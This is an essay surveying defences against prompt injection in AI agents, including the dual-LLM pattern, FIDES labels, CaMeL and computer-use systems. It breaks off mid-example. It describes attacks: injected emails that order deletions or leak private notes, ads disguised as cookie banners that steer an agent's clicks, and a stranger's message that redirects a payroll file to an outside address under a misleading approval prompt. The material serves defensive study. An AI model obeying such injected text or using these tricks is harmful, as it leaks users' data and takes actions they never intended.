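A model that never reads a stranger's email can't follow instructions in it. An agent can therefore use one model to read untrusted text and another, the planner, to decide which tools to call, with ordinary software keeping the text away from the planner. This protection doesn't depend on what either model learned in training, but the planner has to work without seeing much of the material the task is about.

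### Two models and a controller

The programmer Willison (2023), in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, proposed this split. A privileged model receives the user's requests and can call tools. A quarantined model reads untrusted text and has no tools. The controller, which is ordinary software, runs the tools, stores the results and passes requests between the models. If the user asks for a summary of the latest email, the three work together as follows:

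1. The privileged model requests the email. The controller fetches it, stores it under the name $VAR1 and gives the model only that name.
2. The privileged model asks for a summary of $VAR1. The controller replaces the name with the email's text and sends the request to the quarantined model.
3. The quarantined model writes a summary. The controller stores it as $VAR2 and tells the privileged model that it is ready.
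4. The privileged model asks the controller to show $VAR2 to the user.

The variable name works like the question mark in a parameterised query. The privileged model decides where the text goes, and the text cannot affect that decision. If the email contains an order to delete the mailbox, the order may influence the quarantined model's output, but the only possible result is a bad summary.

Willison allows one exception, for when the quarantined model sorts a text into one of several fixed categories. The controller may pass on the answer after checking that it is exactly one of those categories.

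He also calls his solution "pretty bad". It makes assistants harder to build and less pleasant to use, and a single programming mistake that lets untrusted text reach the privileged model removes the protection. A hostile summary can also trick the user, for instance into pasting a block of scrambled private data into a website. Even displaying a picture can leak data, because the picture's web address may contain it.

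The pattern has another weakness when the agent sends out what the quarantined model wrote. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026), a formal analysis of agent defences, describes a case where the quarantined model drafts a reply to an email and also has access to the user's private notes. Without adding a tool call, an injection in the email can make the model quote the notes in the reply, which the agent then sends. The pattern provides control-flow integrity, meaning that untrusted data can't add, remove or reorder the planned actions, but it doesn't control the data those actions carry.

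### Labels and how they spread

To control the data as well, the software has to record where each piece came from and who may see it. Security researchers call this information-flow control and have studied it since the 1970s. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) applied it to agents in FIDES, a system developed at Microsoft.

FIDES gives each piece of data two labels. The integrity label is *trusted* or *untrusted*, and the confidentiality label is *public* or *secret*. Untrusted is stricter than trusted, and secret is stricter than public, because the system has to be more careful with such data. When the system combines two pieces of data, the result takes the stricter label of each kind. This operation is the join, written ⊔:

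```
trusted ⊔ untrusted = untrusted
public  ⊔ secret    = secret
(trusted, secret) ⊔ (untrusted, public) = (untrusted, secret)
```

Labels ordered in this way form a lattice. The same rule applies to labels more detailed than *public* and *secret*. For example, a label can list the people who may read the data, and the join of two labels keeps only the people on both lists. If Ana, Bob and Carol may read one document, and Bob, Carol and Dan may read another, only Bob and Carol may read a summary of both.

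The join rule is restrictive for language models because nobody can reliably tell which parts of a context window influenced a model's answer. FIDES therefore gives the answer the join of the labels of everything in the context. If an agent reads one email from a stranger after fifty trusted messages, the whole context becomes untrusted, and so does every later tool call, even one unrelated to the email. The context stays untrusted because the conversation only grows. If the agent may take important actions only in a trusted context, that one email blocks all of them until the user starts a new conversation.

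Some researchers have tried to relax this rule by identifying the messages that actually influenced an answer and regenerating the answer from only those messages. Costa and colleagues say their framework could accommodate such methods, but FIDES itself uses the strict rule and keeps untrusted text out of the planner's context.

### Three emails and a summary

When a tool returns a result, FIDES compares the label of each part with the label of the planner's context. It passes the planner any part whose label is no stricter than the context's and stores the rest in variables. For example, the planner might receive an email's date, with a variable name in place of the body. The planner therefore gets more information than in Willison's example, where the controller hides the whole email.

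If the planner uses a variable in a tool call, FIDES replaces it with the stored text and its labels. FIDES then checks the call against a policy, and the tool runs only if the call passes. If the call fails the check, FIDES reports the failure to the planner, which can try another approach.

One of the tasks that Costa and colleagues work through is to summarise the latest three emails and send the summary as a Slack message. Suppose that the message is for a colleague called Bob, that a stranger sent one of the emails, and that Bob does not have permission to read that one. A basic planner, which is a single model calling tools in a loop, makes two calls:

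```
read_emails(3)
send_message(to=Bob, message="The three emails say ...")
```

The model wrote the second call after reading the emails, so the entire call is untrusted. The stranger may have influenced the choice of tool, the recipient or the message.

FIDES makes three calls:

```
read_emails(3)                           result stored as EMAILS
query_llm("Summarise these", EMAILS)     result stored as SUMMARY
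send_message(to=Bob, message=SUMMARY)
```

Here `query_llm` sends a question to the quarantined model. The planner chose the tool and the recipient from the user's request alone, so both are trusted. The summary is untrusted, and only people with access to all three emails may read it.

Reading and summarising the emails are harmless, so the policies apply only to the last call. Its fate depends on which policy the administrator has chosen:

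| Policy for sending a message | Basic planner | FIDES |
|---|---|---|
| Every part of the call must be trusted, including the message | Blocks it, because the model had read the emails | Blocks it, because the summary comes from the emails |
| The planner must choose the call in a trusted context | Blocks it | Allows it |
| Every recipient must have permission to read the content | Blocks it, because Bob may not read one email | Blocks it for the same reason |
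| Either a trusted context or permitted recipients is enough | Blocks it | Allows it |

The strictest policy makes the task impossible for both planners. Costa and colleagues used the most permissive policy for messages in their tests, and they counted a message with an untrusted link as failing the check on recipients. This policy lets the user share private material deliberately. If the user asks the agent to send Bob a summary, the agent sends it, but an injected instruction can't make the agent send the same summary to someone without permission to read it.

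The stranger can still spoil the summary. Costa and colleagues give the example of an email that instructs the quarantined model to produce an empty summary. The agent then sends Bob the summary, as the user asked, but it is useless.

### Answers the planner may read

Sometimes the planner's next step depends on the content of the untrusted text. For example, the user may ask the agent to create a calendar event if any of three emails requests a meeting. The planner could inspect the hidden emails, but that would make its whole context untrusted.

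FIDES lets the planner ask the quarantined model a question and restrict the form of the answer, for instance to yes or no. The software enforces this by letting the model choose only tokens that fit the form. When scheduling a meeting, for example, if the answer is yes, the planner asks the quarantined model to extract the date, time and participants into a variable, then passes that variable to the calendar tool without reading it.

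The number of possible answers limits how much information an answer can carry. With N possible answers, the limit is log₂ N bits:

```
yes or no                        log2(2)      = 1 bit
schedule, reply or forward       log2(3)      ≈ 1.58 bits
ten yes-or-no questions          10 × log2(2) = 10 bits
```

One bit is too small to hold an instruction, but it can still be wrong. A stranger can get a meeting added to the user's calendar just by asking for one, and the stranger also supplies the event's details.

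Ten yes-or-no answers can together distinguish 1,024 cases, so whoever controls the answers can steer a long plan down any branch that the planner has provided for. If the answers concern a secret and affect what the agent does in public, they can reveal more than one character of a password.

In FIDES, an answer's label includes its type, so a policy can accept an untrusted yes or no while rejecting an untrusted sentence. But joining two yes-or-no labels produces another yes-or-no label, so the tenth answer has the same label as the first. To limit how much untrusted information gets through in total, a policy would have to count the questions. Costa and colleagues note that the software could keep a record of past actions for policies to consult, which would make counting possible.

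*Preventing Prompt Injection with Type-Directed Privilege Separation* (2025) bases its whole design on restricted answers. Its quarantined agent may send the privileged agent values of approved types, but never free text. It can put other material into variables that the privileged agent does not read.

### How FIDES performed

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo, the benchmark also used for SecPO. Their version has 97 user tasks in four simulated environments: an office workspace, a travel service, a bank and a Slack account. They used two OpenAI models from 2024, GPT-4o and the reasoning model o1, and ran each test five times. The table shows the percentage of tasks completed without an attack, with each environment counting equally.

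| | GPT-4o | o1 |
|---|---|---|
| Basic planner, policies off | 84.3% | 84.0% |
| FIDES, policies off | 60.6% | 77.6% |
| Basic planner, policies on | 41.9% | 44.4% |
| FIDES, policies on | 50.0% | 60.8% |

Costa and colleagues report that, with policies on, FIDES completes 8% more tasks than the basic planner with GPT-4o and 16% more with o1. These differences are in percentage points; the relative increases are about 19% and 37%. The paper also reports that variables and the quarantined model reduce performance by only 6.3% when policies are off. That figure is also in percentage points and applies only to o1. GPT-4o lost 23.7 points, largely because it used the variables inconsistently.

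The full utility lost to the protection is the difference between a basic planner with no policies and FIDES with policies on. That difference is 34 points with GPT-4o and 23 with o1, more than the "modest loss in utility" that the researchers describe in their conclusion.

The averages combine very different results across environments. The basic planner beat FIDES on travel tasks with both models, because the policies allow many travel tools to run in an untrusted context as long as no private data leaks. In banking, many tasks require the agent to read a file and follow its instructions, and the policies block the resulting payments by design.

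The researchers ran the security tests with GPT-4o and put AgentDojo's fixed attacks into the data. With policies off, 152 injections succeeded against the basic planner and 21 against FIDES, which could inspect a variable and then act on what it had read. With policies on, the researchers counted no successful attacks against either planner. Using fixed attacks is less of a weakness here than in tests of trained models, because the policy check depends on labels, which don't change when an attack is reworded.

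The count of zero depends on what qualifies as a successful attack. AgentDojo's scoring recorded three successes against FIDES and 20 against the basic planner. Costa and colleagues excluded cases where the policy stopped the tool from running, where the policy permitted the action, or where the injection changed only the agent's wording. One injection of the last kind makes the agent recommend a particular place, which a traveller who wanted honest advice would probably consider a successful attack.

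The researchers also made the labelling easier than it would be in practice. They marked a field as untrusted if at least one AgentDojo attack targeted it, but someone running a real agent doesn't know in advance which fields attackers will target.

The test policies for payments and other important actions checked only whether the planner had chosen the call in a trusted context and ignored the labels on the arguments. If a user asks FIDES to pay a bill stored in a file, the planner chooses to make a payment, uses the quarantined model to extract the account number, and passes the number to the bank in a variable. If a criminal has changed the number in the file, the policy still allows the payment. A stricter policy that also required the account number to be trusted would block this payment, but it would block payments of genuine bills too.

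### What the guarantee leaves out

The confidentiality guarantee that Costa and colleagues establish for FIDES is called explicit secrecy. Take any sequence of actions that the agent might carry out, and let g be the combined effect of those actions on the stored data. If two starting states d₁ and d₂ have the same public data, then the public data must also be the same afterwards:

```
if public(d1) = public(d2), then public(g(d1)) = public(g(d2))
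```

Changing only the secrets therefore can't change what an outsider reads in the public data, as long as the agent takes the same actions. But a secret may leak by affecting which actions the agent takes, which is called an implicit flow. Suppose a user asks an agent to read a medical test result and book an appointment at a clinic if the result is positive. The booking contains no text from the result, so explicit secrecy allows it, but anyone who can see the clinic's calendar can work out the result.

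A stronger property, non-interference, also rules out implicit flows. Costa and colleagues rejected it as too restrictive, because an agent that had used a tool to read something secret could then use almost no tools that write public data. Their guarantee also doesn't cover side channels, such as the timing of the agent's actions or the size of its network messages.

*On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* confirms that labels that track only data are not enough for every plan, because a plan can branch on a private value. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026), which presents a formal language for describing agents, notes that most information-flow systems tolerate a leak of at least one bit per run. It focuses more on how designers relax a guarantee to keep a system usable, for example by allowing restricted answers, and recommends that reviewers examine these exceptions closely.

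The design can't handle some tasks, such as following a website's installation guide, because the untrusted text contains the steps. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026), which adapts the dual-model pattern to agents that operate a screen, acknowledges this limit. The planner can't plan the installation without reading the guide, but reading it makes the planner's context untrusted, and the policy then blocks the important steps.

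The guarantee also assumes correct labels. FIDES treats everything the user enters as trusted, including text pasted from a stranger's message. It labels an email's sender and recipients as its only readers, although someone may have forwarded it to others.

### CaMeL and plans written as code

Debenedetti and colleagues, including researchers at Google DeepMind, published a related system called CaMeL a few months before FIDES. According to *CaMeLoT* (2026), CaMeL's privileged model turns the user's request into a complete program in a restricted version of Python. An interpreter runs the program and calls the quarantined model whenever it needs information from untrusted text. The interpreter also tags each value with its sources and permitted readers, and checks these tags against a policy before each tool call. CaMeL's developers call the tags capabilities, but they are closer to the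 labels in FIDES than to the unforgeable references in KeyKOS.

The privileged model writes the program before anything has read the untrusted data, so an injection can't add a call to the program. The tags matter just as much. *Language-Based Agent Control* (2026) notes that CaMeL without policies still has two models but does not check the flow of data, so the quarantined model could again leak private notes in a reply. CaMeL also has a strict mode in which a value's tags depend on the decisions that led to it as well as on its data. This mode is meant to prevent implicit flows like the one in the clinic example.

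A program written in advance can't easily handle unexpected results. If a tool returns an error or a document requires another search, CaMeL's planner can't read the result and revise its plan, whereas FIDES can inspect a variable and accept the stricter label.

*Language-Based Agent Control* is more flexible because it treats the dual-model pattern as only one way to use labels. An agent that has read untrusted text can keep its tools, and the labels determine which calls it may still make. For example, it might be able to search the web again after reading a suspicious page but not to send money.

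### Planning around the policy

FIDES's planner has no access to the policies it must satisfy, so it may inspect a variable it could have left hidden and then be unable to send a message or make a payment. In *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026), Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues extended FIDES to avoid this. Several of them had worked on the original system.

Their agent, Prudentia, shows the planner which policy applies to each tool and whether the planner's context is still trusted. Before inspecting a variable, the planner has to explain why it needs to and what it will do next. It can also ask the user to endorse, or vouch for, a piece of untrusted text. If an email lists ten jobs, one endorsement lets the agent do them all, while FIDES would need approval for each one. But the user then has to judge the whole email, and whether people do that well is a separate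 question.

Kolluri and colleagues argue that earlier comparisons were unfair to systems like FIDES. The basic planner scored well because the tests let it act freely, whereas many real products ask the user to approve every important action. They therefore measured how many AgentDojo tasks each agent could complete with no approvals at all, assuming that the basic agent must request one for each important action. With GPT-5, they found:

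| | Tasks completed with no approvals | Tasks completed with unlimited approvals | Approvals used in all completed tasks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Basic agent | 35.1% | 72.3% | 52.0 |
| FIDES | 57.1% | 78.9% | 41.3 |
| Prudentia | 72.7% | 80.0% | 7.3 |

This comparison is reasonable for products that ask for approval. For an agent that runs unattended, the gap between FIDES and an undefended planner remains.

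Prudentia's advantage also depends on the model. With GPT-4o, it completed 42.5% of tasks without approvals, compared with 50.3% for FIDES. It also cost about 1.9 to 2.5 times as much per task as FIDES with that model, although the researchers had not tried to reduce the cost.

Microsoft now documents FIDES as part of its Agent Framework, a toolkit for building agents. Microsoft's *information flow control moving toward secure autonomous agents* describes how tools can attach labels to their results through the Model Context Protocol, a common standard for connecting agents to tools. Programs that do not understand the labels can ignore them, which makes adoption easier but leaves those programs without the labels' protection.

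### A reader and an actor in OpenClaw

Some developers give the two agents separate tools but let text pass between them. Cheng and Tsao (2026) tested a version of this in *Agent Privilege Separation in OpenClaw*. One agent reads the emails and writes a summary, and another reads the summary and can send email. Cheng and Tsao also tried making the first agent write its summary as structured data (JSON), with separate fields for the sender, the subject, the content and any tasks.

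Their attacks came from a public Microsoft competition. They started with 22,899 different attacks and ran them against a single agent using the model GPT-5-mini, which resisted all but 649. They then tested their defences on those 649:

| Defence | Successful attacks | Success rate |
|---|---|---|
| Single agent (used to select the attacks) | 649 | 100% |
| Single agent with JSON summaries | 92 | 14.18% |
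| Two agents | 2 | 0.31% |
| Two agents with JSON summaries | 0 | 0% |

Separating the tools clearly did more than changing the format, but the size of the improvement is hard to judge. Cheng and Tsao chose attacks that had worked once against the single agent. Models do not always respond to the same input in the same way, so some of these attacks might have failed on a second attempt without any new defence.

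The attacks were also static. They were written to fool one agent, and nobody adapted them to survive a summary and then influence a second agent. Cheng and Tsao acknowledge this limit, but they also claim that the sending agent never receives raw injected content. That is true of the original email but misleading about the summaries. Injected material got into 63.7% of the summaries in the full version, and the filter meant to catch it only recorded it without blocking it. The sending agent ignored the material each time, so part of the protection still came from the model's own resistance. Following Willison's rule that free text from the quarantined model must never reach the privileged one would have removed this dependence.

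### Short hints in Twin Agent

*Twin Agent* (Hu, Jacob and colleagues, 2026) deliberately lets free text through but limits its length. Its Explore Agent reads everything, including untrusted text, but cannot take privileged actions. The Safe Agent can act but does not read the untrusted text. At each step, the Explore Agent looks at what the Safe Agent has done so far and may send it a hint about what to do next, limited to 100 or 200 characters depending on the task. A separate detector blocks hints that look like injections.

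The design relies on the observation that successful injections against recent models tend to be long. A useful hint, such as the name of the buggy function, can be very short because the Safe Agent already has the rest of the context.

Hu and colleagues tested Twin Agent on 232 real software bugs, adding malicious instructions to the bug reports. Using GPT-5.2, an ordinary agent fixed 61.2% of the bugs and followed the malicious instructions 97.0% of the time. Twin Agent fixed 62.5% and never followed them. A strict two-agent design with no hints fixed none, because the agent making the repair had no information about the bug.

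Using Gemini 2.5 Flash, Twin Agent completed 62.9% of the tasks on AgentDojo, compared with 61.9% for an undefended agent and 30.9% for CaMeL. The researchers had cut CaMeL's retry limit per task from ten to three, but they say its original developers reported a completion rate of only about 35%. On the Slack tasks, however, Twin Agent completed 66.7%, compared with 90.5% for the undefended agent.

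The researchers also attacked their own system using their knowledge of how it worked. They used another model to search for short hints that might persuade the Safe Agent to do something harmful, then wrote bug reports telling the Explore Agent to copy one out. In separate tests, the Explore Agent copied the hint every time. In the complete system, the detector let malicious hints through in 57 of 232 cases, and the Safe Agent carried out the attack in 11 (4.7% of the 232). They reran those 11 cases five times each and none succeeded again, so chance seems to play a large part. However, an attacker can get more chances by filing many bug reports.

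Hu and colleagues state that Twin Agent has no formal guarantee. A hint of 100 keyboard characters can carry up to about 657 bits, compared with one bit for a yes-or-no answer, which is enough for an order to delete a file. The limit applies to each hint separately, and a long task allows many hints. The researchers did not search for attacks that build up over several hints because this would have cost too much. In the software tests, the Safe Agent could also read the code repository directly, so someone who planted instructions there could reach it without a hint.

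## Agents that operate a screen

The agents described so far call tools with names such as `send_message`, and software can check each call because its name and arguments show what it does. Many programs offer no such tools, so a computer-use agent operates them by looking at screenshots and using the mouse and keyboard. This lets it work with almost any program, but makes labels and policies like those in FIDES much harder to apply.

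### A click has no fixed meaning

A policy that lets an agent click permits any action a click can trigger. A call to `click(640, 380)` may log the user in, delete a file or open an attacker's website, depending on what is at that point on the screen, whereas a call to `send_email(to, subject, body)` always sends an email.

The agent also has to look at the screen to see where to click. Software can store the body of an email separately and hide it from the planner, but a screenshot is one image that mixes the browser's buttons with advertisements and strangers' comments. An ordinary computer-use agent takes a screenshot, chooses an action, then takes another screenshot, so a stranger's text can reach the planner at any step. A planner that never sees the screen would avoid this, but it seems unable to choose its next action.

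### A program written before the first look

Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) showed in *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* that such a planner can still do some useful work. They adapted CaMeL, in which the planner writes a program before anything reads untrusted data. The planner can't predict exactly what a screen will look like, but there are usually only a few possible situations at each step, such as the browser being open or closed. It can therefore write instructions for each situation in advance, which Foerster and colleagues call single-shot planning.

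In the CaMeL-NOVA system, the planner writes the program and then takes no further part. As the program runs, it queries a quarantined vision model about what is on the screen, and the interpreter uses the answers to choose between branches.

Suppose the user asks for this month's weather forecast for Manchester. The weather site may or may not cover its page with a cookie banner, so the planner has to allow for both. In simplified form, that part of the program looks like this:

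```
screen = describe_screen()
if verify(screen, "a cookie banner is visible") is OK:
    for name in ["Accept all", "I agree", "OK"]:
        if no button has worked yet:
            position = find(name)
            if position was found:
                click(position)
continue to the forecast
```

1. The vision model describes the screen.
2. A quarantined language model compares the description with the planner's statement about a cookie banner and answers OK, FAIL or UNKNOWN.
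3. If the answer is OK, the interpreter enters the branch and asks the vision model for the coordinates of each button in turn.
4. The interpreter clicks on a button it has found and checks whether the screen has changed. If it hasn't, the program can try the next name.

If the banner contains an order to email the user's passwords to a stranger, the planner never reads it, and the program has no step that sends email.

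NOVA stands for "Navigating via Observation, Verification, and Action", the pattern that these steps follow. Foerster and colleagues noticed this pattern in successful plans and added it to the planner's standing instructions, together with routines for common problems such as cookie banners and failed clicks. Given three attempts at each of 60 tasks, the system solved 35 with these instructions and 11 without them.

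### Plans made largely of fallbacks

Planning for unseen screens makes the programs much longer than those CaMeL writes for AgentDojo, where tools return structured data:

| Average per plan | CaMeL on AgentDojo | Screen agent without NOVA | CaMeL-NOVA |
|---|---|---|---|
| Lines of code | 51.8 | 71.6 | 213.3 |
| Tool calls | 4.9 | 19.8 | 41.1 |
| Branches | 3.7 | 11.3 | 39.7 |
| Branches that depend on a quarantined model's output | 1.9 | 7.9 | 24.2 |

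About half the steps in a CaMeL-NOVA plan are fallbacks that do not run. The last row, which matters most for security, shows that an average plan has about 24 points where a quarantined model's report about the screen affects the choice of action. The fallbacks that make the agent more useful therefore also give an attacker more decisions to influence.

### What the OSWorld figures count

Foerster and colleagues tested the system on OSWorld, a benchmark of 369 tasks in programs such as Chrome and LibreOffice. They report that it retains up to 57% of a frontier model's performance. This figure comes from 109 tasks with Claude Sonnet 4.5 as the vision model. The system solved 31 of them on the first attempt and 62 within five attempts.

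The researchers tested each vision model only on tasks it had already solved on its own, in one run of at most 15 steps. The unprotected model therefore scores 100% on its task set.

| Vision model | Tasks it had solved alone | Solved by CaMeL-NOVA on the first attempt | Solved within five attempts |
|---|---|---|---|
| UI-TARS-1.5-7B | 60 | 25 (41.7%) | 39 (65.0%) |
| OpenCUA-32B | 76 | 22 (28.9%) | 48 (63.2%) |
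| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 109 | 31 (28.4%) | 62 (56.9%) |

This selection is partly unfair to CaMeL-NOVA, because some of the original successes were probably lucky and the unprotected models might not repeat them. But the five-attempt figures favour CaMeL-NOVA, because the unprotected models had only one attempt. Those figures are also relevant only if someone can pick out the successful attempt. A benchmark can reset the machine after each failure, but on a real computer a failed attempt may already have sent a message or deleted a file.

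The researchers also ran CaMeL-NOVA with UI-TARS, a small open model, on the whole benchmark. They report a success rate of 29.0%, compared with 24.4% for UI-TARS alone, and so claim a 19% improvement. Both figures include 30 tasks that OSWorld cannot score automatically and counts as solved by default. On the other 339 tasks, CaMeL-NOVA solved 77 (22.7%) within three attempts, and UI-TARS alone solved 60 (17.7%) in one. On its first attempt, CaMeL-NOVA solved 51 (15.0%), slightly fewer than the unprotected UI-TARS, although CaMeL-NOVA had a much stronger model to plan for it.

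Two other groups have since tested the design. Seip, Markovinović and Hein (2026), in *Towards Safe Autonomy for Computer Use*, found that it completed 8.3% of 36 OSWorld tasks, compared with 58.3% for an unprotected agent. Choudhary, Christodorescu and colleagues (2026), in *Secure-CUA*, measured an average of 13.17% on 400 web tasks, compared with 55.12% without protection. Both groups were promoting rival systems and used different models, but their results are close to the 15.0% that CaMeL-NOVA achieved on its first attempt at the whole benchmark. The 15.0% is probably a better guide to its usefulness than the 57%.

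Most of the system's ability comes from the planner. Changing the vision model hardly affected the results on the 60 UI-TARS tasks, where the system solved 39, 40 or 41 within five attempts, depending on the model. On a smaller set of 17 tasks, the system solved 12 with GPT-5 as the planner but only four with the weakest planners.

CaMeL-NOVA used 1.88 times as many tokens as the unprotected agent on those 17 tasks. A version based on FIDES used 29.6 times as many, because it calls the planner with the full history at every step instead of only once. Both protected totals include up to five attempts at each task. The FIDES version performed about as well, solving 40 of the 60 UI-TARS tasks within five attempts. To make it work, Foerster and colleagues had to let its planner read yes-or-no answers about the screen. They limited how much information the planner received by capping the number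 of steps and the number of times it could reuse an answer.

### Branch steering

An attacker cannot add an action to a CaMeL-NOVA plan, but can influence which of the prepared branches runs. Foerster and colleagues call this branch steering.

In the paper's main example, an attacker buys an advertisement and disguises it as a cookie banner. The program uses a vision model to check for a cookie banner, and the result is positive. It then requests the position of the "Accept" button and receives a point inside the advertisement. The interpreter clicks there, exactly as the plan specifies, and the browser opens the attacker's website. The trick resembles the false windows that programs can paint to fool people, but its target is a vision model.

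Cookie banners are a good target because almost every plan for a web task checks for them, so the attacker does not need to know much about the task. Each check covers whatever is on the screen at the time, including a later page that the attacker expects the agent to visit.

More serious harm depends more on which steps the plan already includes. An attacker can redirect a payment only if the plan includes one and the user is logged in to the bank. The attacker must also corrupt at least two of the vision model's answers consistently, such as the positions of the recipient field and the confirm button. Stealing data requires a plan that reads something private and sends something out. Single-shot planning therefore still prevents much of this harm, because most tasks include neither a payment nor a message.

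Control-flow integrity limits an agent to its planned actions but doesn't protect the values that determine which of those actions it takes. Suppose an agent's plan is to buy a kettle if it costs no more than $50. An attacker who controls the displayed price can't make the agent buy a television, but can make it buy an $80 kettle by showing a price of $45. If a program has no branches, a false value can only corrupt an argument, such as the text of a message, but in a program with 40 branches it can also determine what the agent does next.

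Even the guarantee about actions is weaker on a screen, because it covers calls such as `click`, but the effect of a click depends on where it lands. If the vision model returns the wrong coordinates, a planned click may press a button that wasn't in the plan.

### Two checks that failed

Foerster and colleagues tried to catch false answers by adding a second source of information. One check compared the vision model's answer with the page's underlying structure, which often labels advertisements. The other gave the screenshot and the answer to a second vision model from a different company, on the theory that a picture made to fool one model would probably not fool the other.

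Both checks failed. Some advertising formats let the advertiser supply part of the page's structure, so the advertiser can also label a false banner as a cookie banner in that structure. A specially altered picture got past the second model by making the first model choose the wrong link and give a plausible reason for it.

The checks also interfered with ordinary work. The structure check flagged six of ten cookie attacks and raised false alarms on four of 17 harmless tasks. The second model flagged five of ten attacks and raised false alarms on three of the 17 tasks. These samples are small. Almost all the false alarms came from mistaking a genuine cookie banner for a fake, and each false alarm ends the task. Real banners and good imitations look alike, so a check strict enough to stop every imitation will also stop many real banners. Adding the second model also raised token use to 6.57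 times that of the unprotected agent.

A narrower search sometimes worked better. Some plans searched only for buttons, which advertisers cannot create in the simpler advertising format, so the attack failed without any model having to recognise it as fake.

### Limits on each branch

*Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks* (Zingrillo, Foerster and colleagues, 2026) presents COBRA, a system that focuses on limiting what a branch can do once an attacker has steered the agent into it. Before the agent looks at the screen, COBRA also writes a branching program, and its planner attaches limits to each branch, such as which websites it may contact and which values it may send.

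COBRA checks these limits in the network traffic, because the web request a click triggers often has a fixed meaning even though the click itself does not. All the agent's requests pass through a proxy, which blocks any that the current branch does not allow. If the user asks the agent to comment on a software issue, for example, the proxy lets it read issues and post comments. If the agent clicks a false button that would give a stranger access to the code, the proxy blocks the request, even though it goes to the same website.

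Such precise checks require a sitemap, a list of the site's operations that the user has approved. Without one, the proxy can restrict only which websites the agent contacts. In a test on an existing benchmark, COBRA without sitemaps blocked all five attacks that went to another website but none of the 14 that misused the website the agent was already using. With sitemaps, it blocked all 19. Websites rarely publish these lists. Zingrillo and colleagues wrote a program that drafts them, and for 18 of 25 web tasks its drafts covered every operation needed.

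On the team's own benchmark, attacks succeeded 89.5% of the time against the earlier design and never against COBRA. The benchmark counts an attack as successful if the harmful action breaks the limits in force. The result therefore shows that COBRA enforces its limits, but is weaker evidence about whether the planner chose the right ones.

Zingrillo and colleagues define *data-flow integrity* as a guarantee that untrusted data cannot influence which branch runs or set the important values. COBRA's guarantee is weaker because untrusted data may still choose a branch or fill in a value if the result stays within the limits. An agent that has to react to prices or search results probably can't avoid this. The proxy also can't check a price that never appears in the request, determine whether a permitted comment is offensive, or inspect email and file operations that bypass it.

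COBRA's planner still works without seeing the screen. With Claude Sonnet 5 both planning and reading the screen, COBRA completed 38.8% of 361 tasks within five attempts, while the same model working normally completed 51.0%. To avoid choosing among attempts afterwards, the planner can write five plans and merge them into one program before the agent starts. With UI-TARS as the vision model, this raised the number of tasks solved on the first attempt from 78 to 105 and the cost of planning from $0.33 to $0.59 per task.

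### Letting the planner see part of the screen

Other researchers let the planner see part of the page. In *Untrusted Content Masking for Web Agents with Security Guarantees*, Nikolić, Zverev and colleagues (2026) replace reviews, advertisements and other untrusted content with labelled boxes. The planner can see the menus and buttons around the boxes and can revise its plan as it goes. If it needs information from a box, it queries a quarantined model that can return only a restricted answer, as in FIDES.

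This approach relies on the website's owner to mark the untrusted parts. Nikolić and colleagues labelled three real websites by hand and found that 15 to 30 rules per site were enough. A language model can also write the rules, but when Seip and colleagues tested this, 37% to 44% of the untrusted free text stayed visible. They defined untrusted text more broadly than the method's designers did, which makes the result look somewhat worse.

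Seip and colleagues reverse the default in their own system, SA-CUA, which hides everything on a page or in a document except what its rules identify as safe. On 160 hand-labelled screens, it let no untrusted free text through, but it also hid more than half of the trusted elements. It completed 31% to 39% of the 36 OSWorld tasks, compared with 8.3% for the blind planner.

Even a yes-or-no answer can determine which branch of a plan the agent follows, so SA-CUA also checks a value before the planner may rely on it. Suppose the user wants a Python package that prints coloured text, and a forum post recommends one called termcolor. A component that has not seen the post works out the expected name from trusted sources, such as the planner's own knowledge, and ordinary software compares the two names. An attacker can cause a mismatch, which stops the agent from using the name, but can't get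 a different name accepted. The check depends on reliable sources, and SA-CUA treats GitHub as an authority even though anyone can publish there.

Choudhary and colleagues separate choosing an action from finding its target on the screen. If the user asks an agent to copy a review into a product's Description field, an instruction in the review might cause the agent to choose the Title field instead. An agent that correctly chooses Description might still click on Title if a misleading advertisement causes the vision model to misidentify the field. Their system, Secure-CUA, hides untrusted areas during both stages and writes a new short program for each action, so it can adapt to what has happened. In runs without attacks, it completed 53.55% of 400 web tasks, almost as many as the unprotected agent. The proof of security assumes that the system has correctly labelled everything an attacker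 controls.

Some information can't be checked against an independent source. If a user asks an agent to find a laptop in good condition and buy it, the seller's description may be the only evidence of its condition. SA-CUA can't complete such a purchase safely on its own. One version of Nikolić and colleagues' system makes an exception and lets the quarantined model pass free text to the planner if the user reads and approves it first. In tests on a copy of the software-hosting site GitLab, this let the agent complete the tasks it had failed because of masking.

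## Asking the user to approve an agent's action

When software can't determine whether an agent's action is safe, it usually prompts the user for approval. For example, a coding agent may request approval before running a command, and an email assistant before sending a message. The prompt needs a trusted path in both directions, because the user has to see the system's own description of the action and the system has to receive the user's own answer.

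A program outside the model should display the approval dialog and receive the user's click. If the agent asks "Shall I send it?" in the conversation and the user types "yes", the answer becomes more text in the context window, and the model decides what that answer permits. An injected sentence claiming that the user has already agreed might have the same effect. With a dialog like the one dom0 displays for qrexec requests, the program holds the agent's call until the user clicks, and no text in the context window can approve the call.

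The agent must also be unable to tamper with that software. Pirch and colleagues compare the model to an untrusted user and the runtime, the software that runs the agent, to an operating system's kernel. But in many agents, such as OpenClaw, the tools run with the same privileges as the code that is supposed to restrict them. An agent that can run any shell command may be able to edit the settings that determine when it has to ask for approval.

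### A request to send a file

Suppose Ana asks an agent to send the quarterly budget to Maria, her accountant. The agent searches her mail for the address and finds a message from a stranger. It claims that Maria has a new address and that the budget is now in a file called `payroll.xlsx`. The model believes both claims and prepares this call:

```
send_file(path="Documents/payroll.xlsx", to="maria@northgate-billing.example")
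```

The software holds the agent's tool call and shows Ana an approval prompt, but the model writes the prompt's text: "Send the quarterly budget to Maria, as you asked?" The call actually sends everybody's salary details to a stranger, and it runs when Ana clicks Allow.

The prompt and Ana's click are both genuine, but the model read the stranger's message before writing the description, so the stranger influenced both what the agent did and what Ana read. The Qubes dialog omits the file's name, whereas this prompt gives Ana false information about the file.

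Attackers have exploited the user's role in such decisions outside the laboratory. *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues, 2025) analyses 11 attacks on real agents and marks the human as a weak link in two of them.

Ordinary code can instead fill in the prompt from the call itself:

```
Tool        send_file
File        Documents/payroll.xlsx
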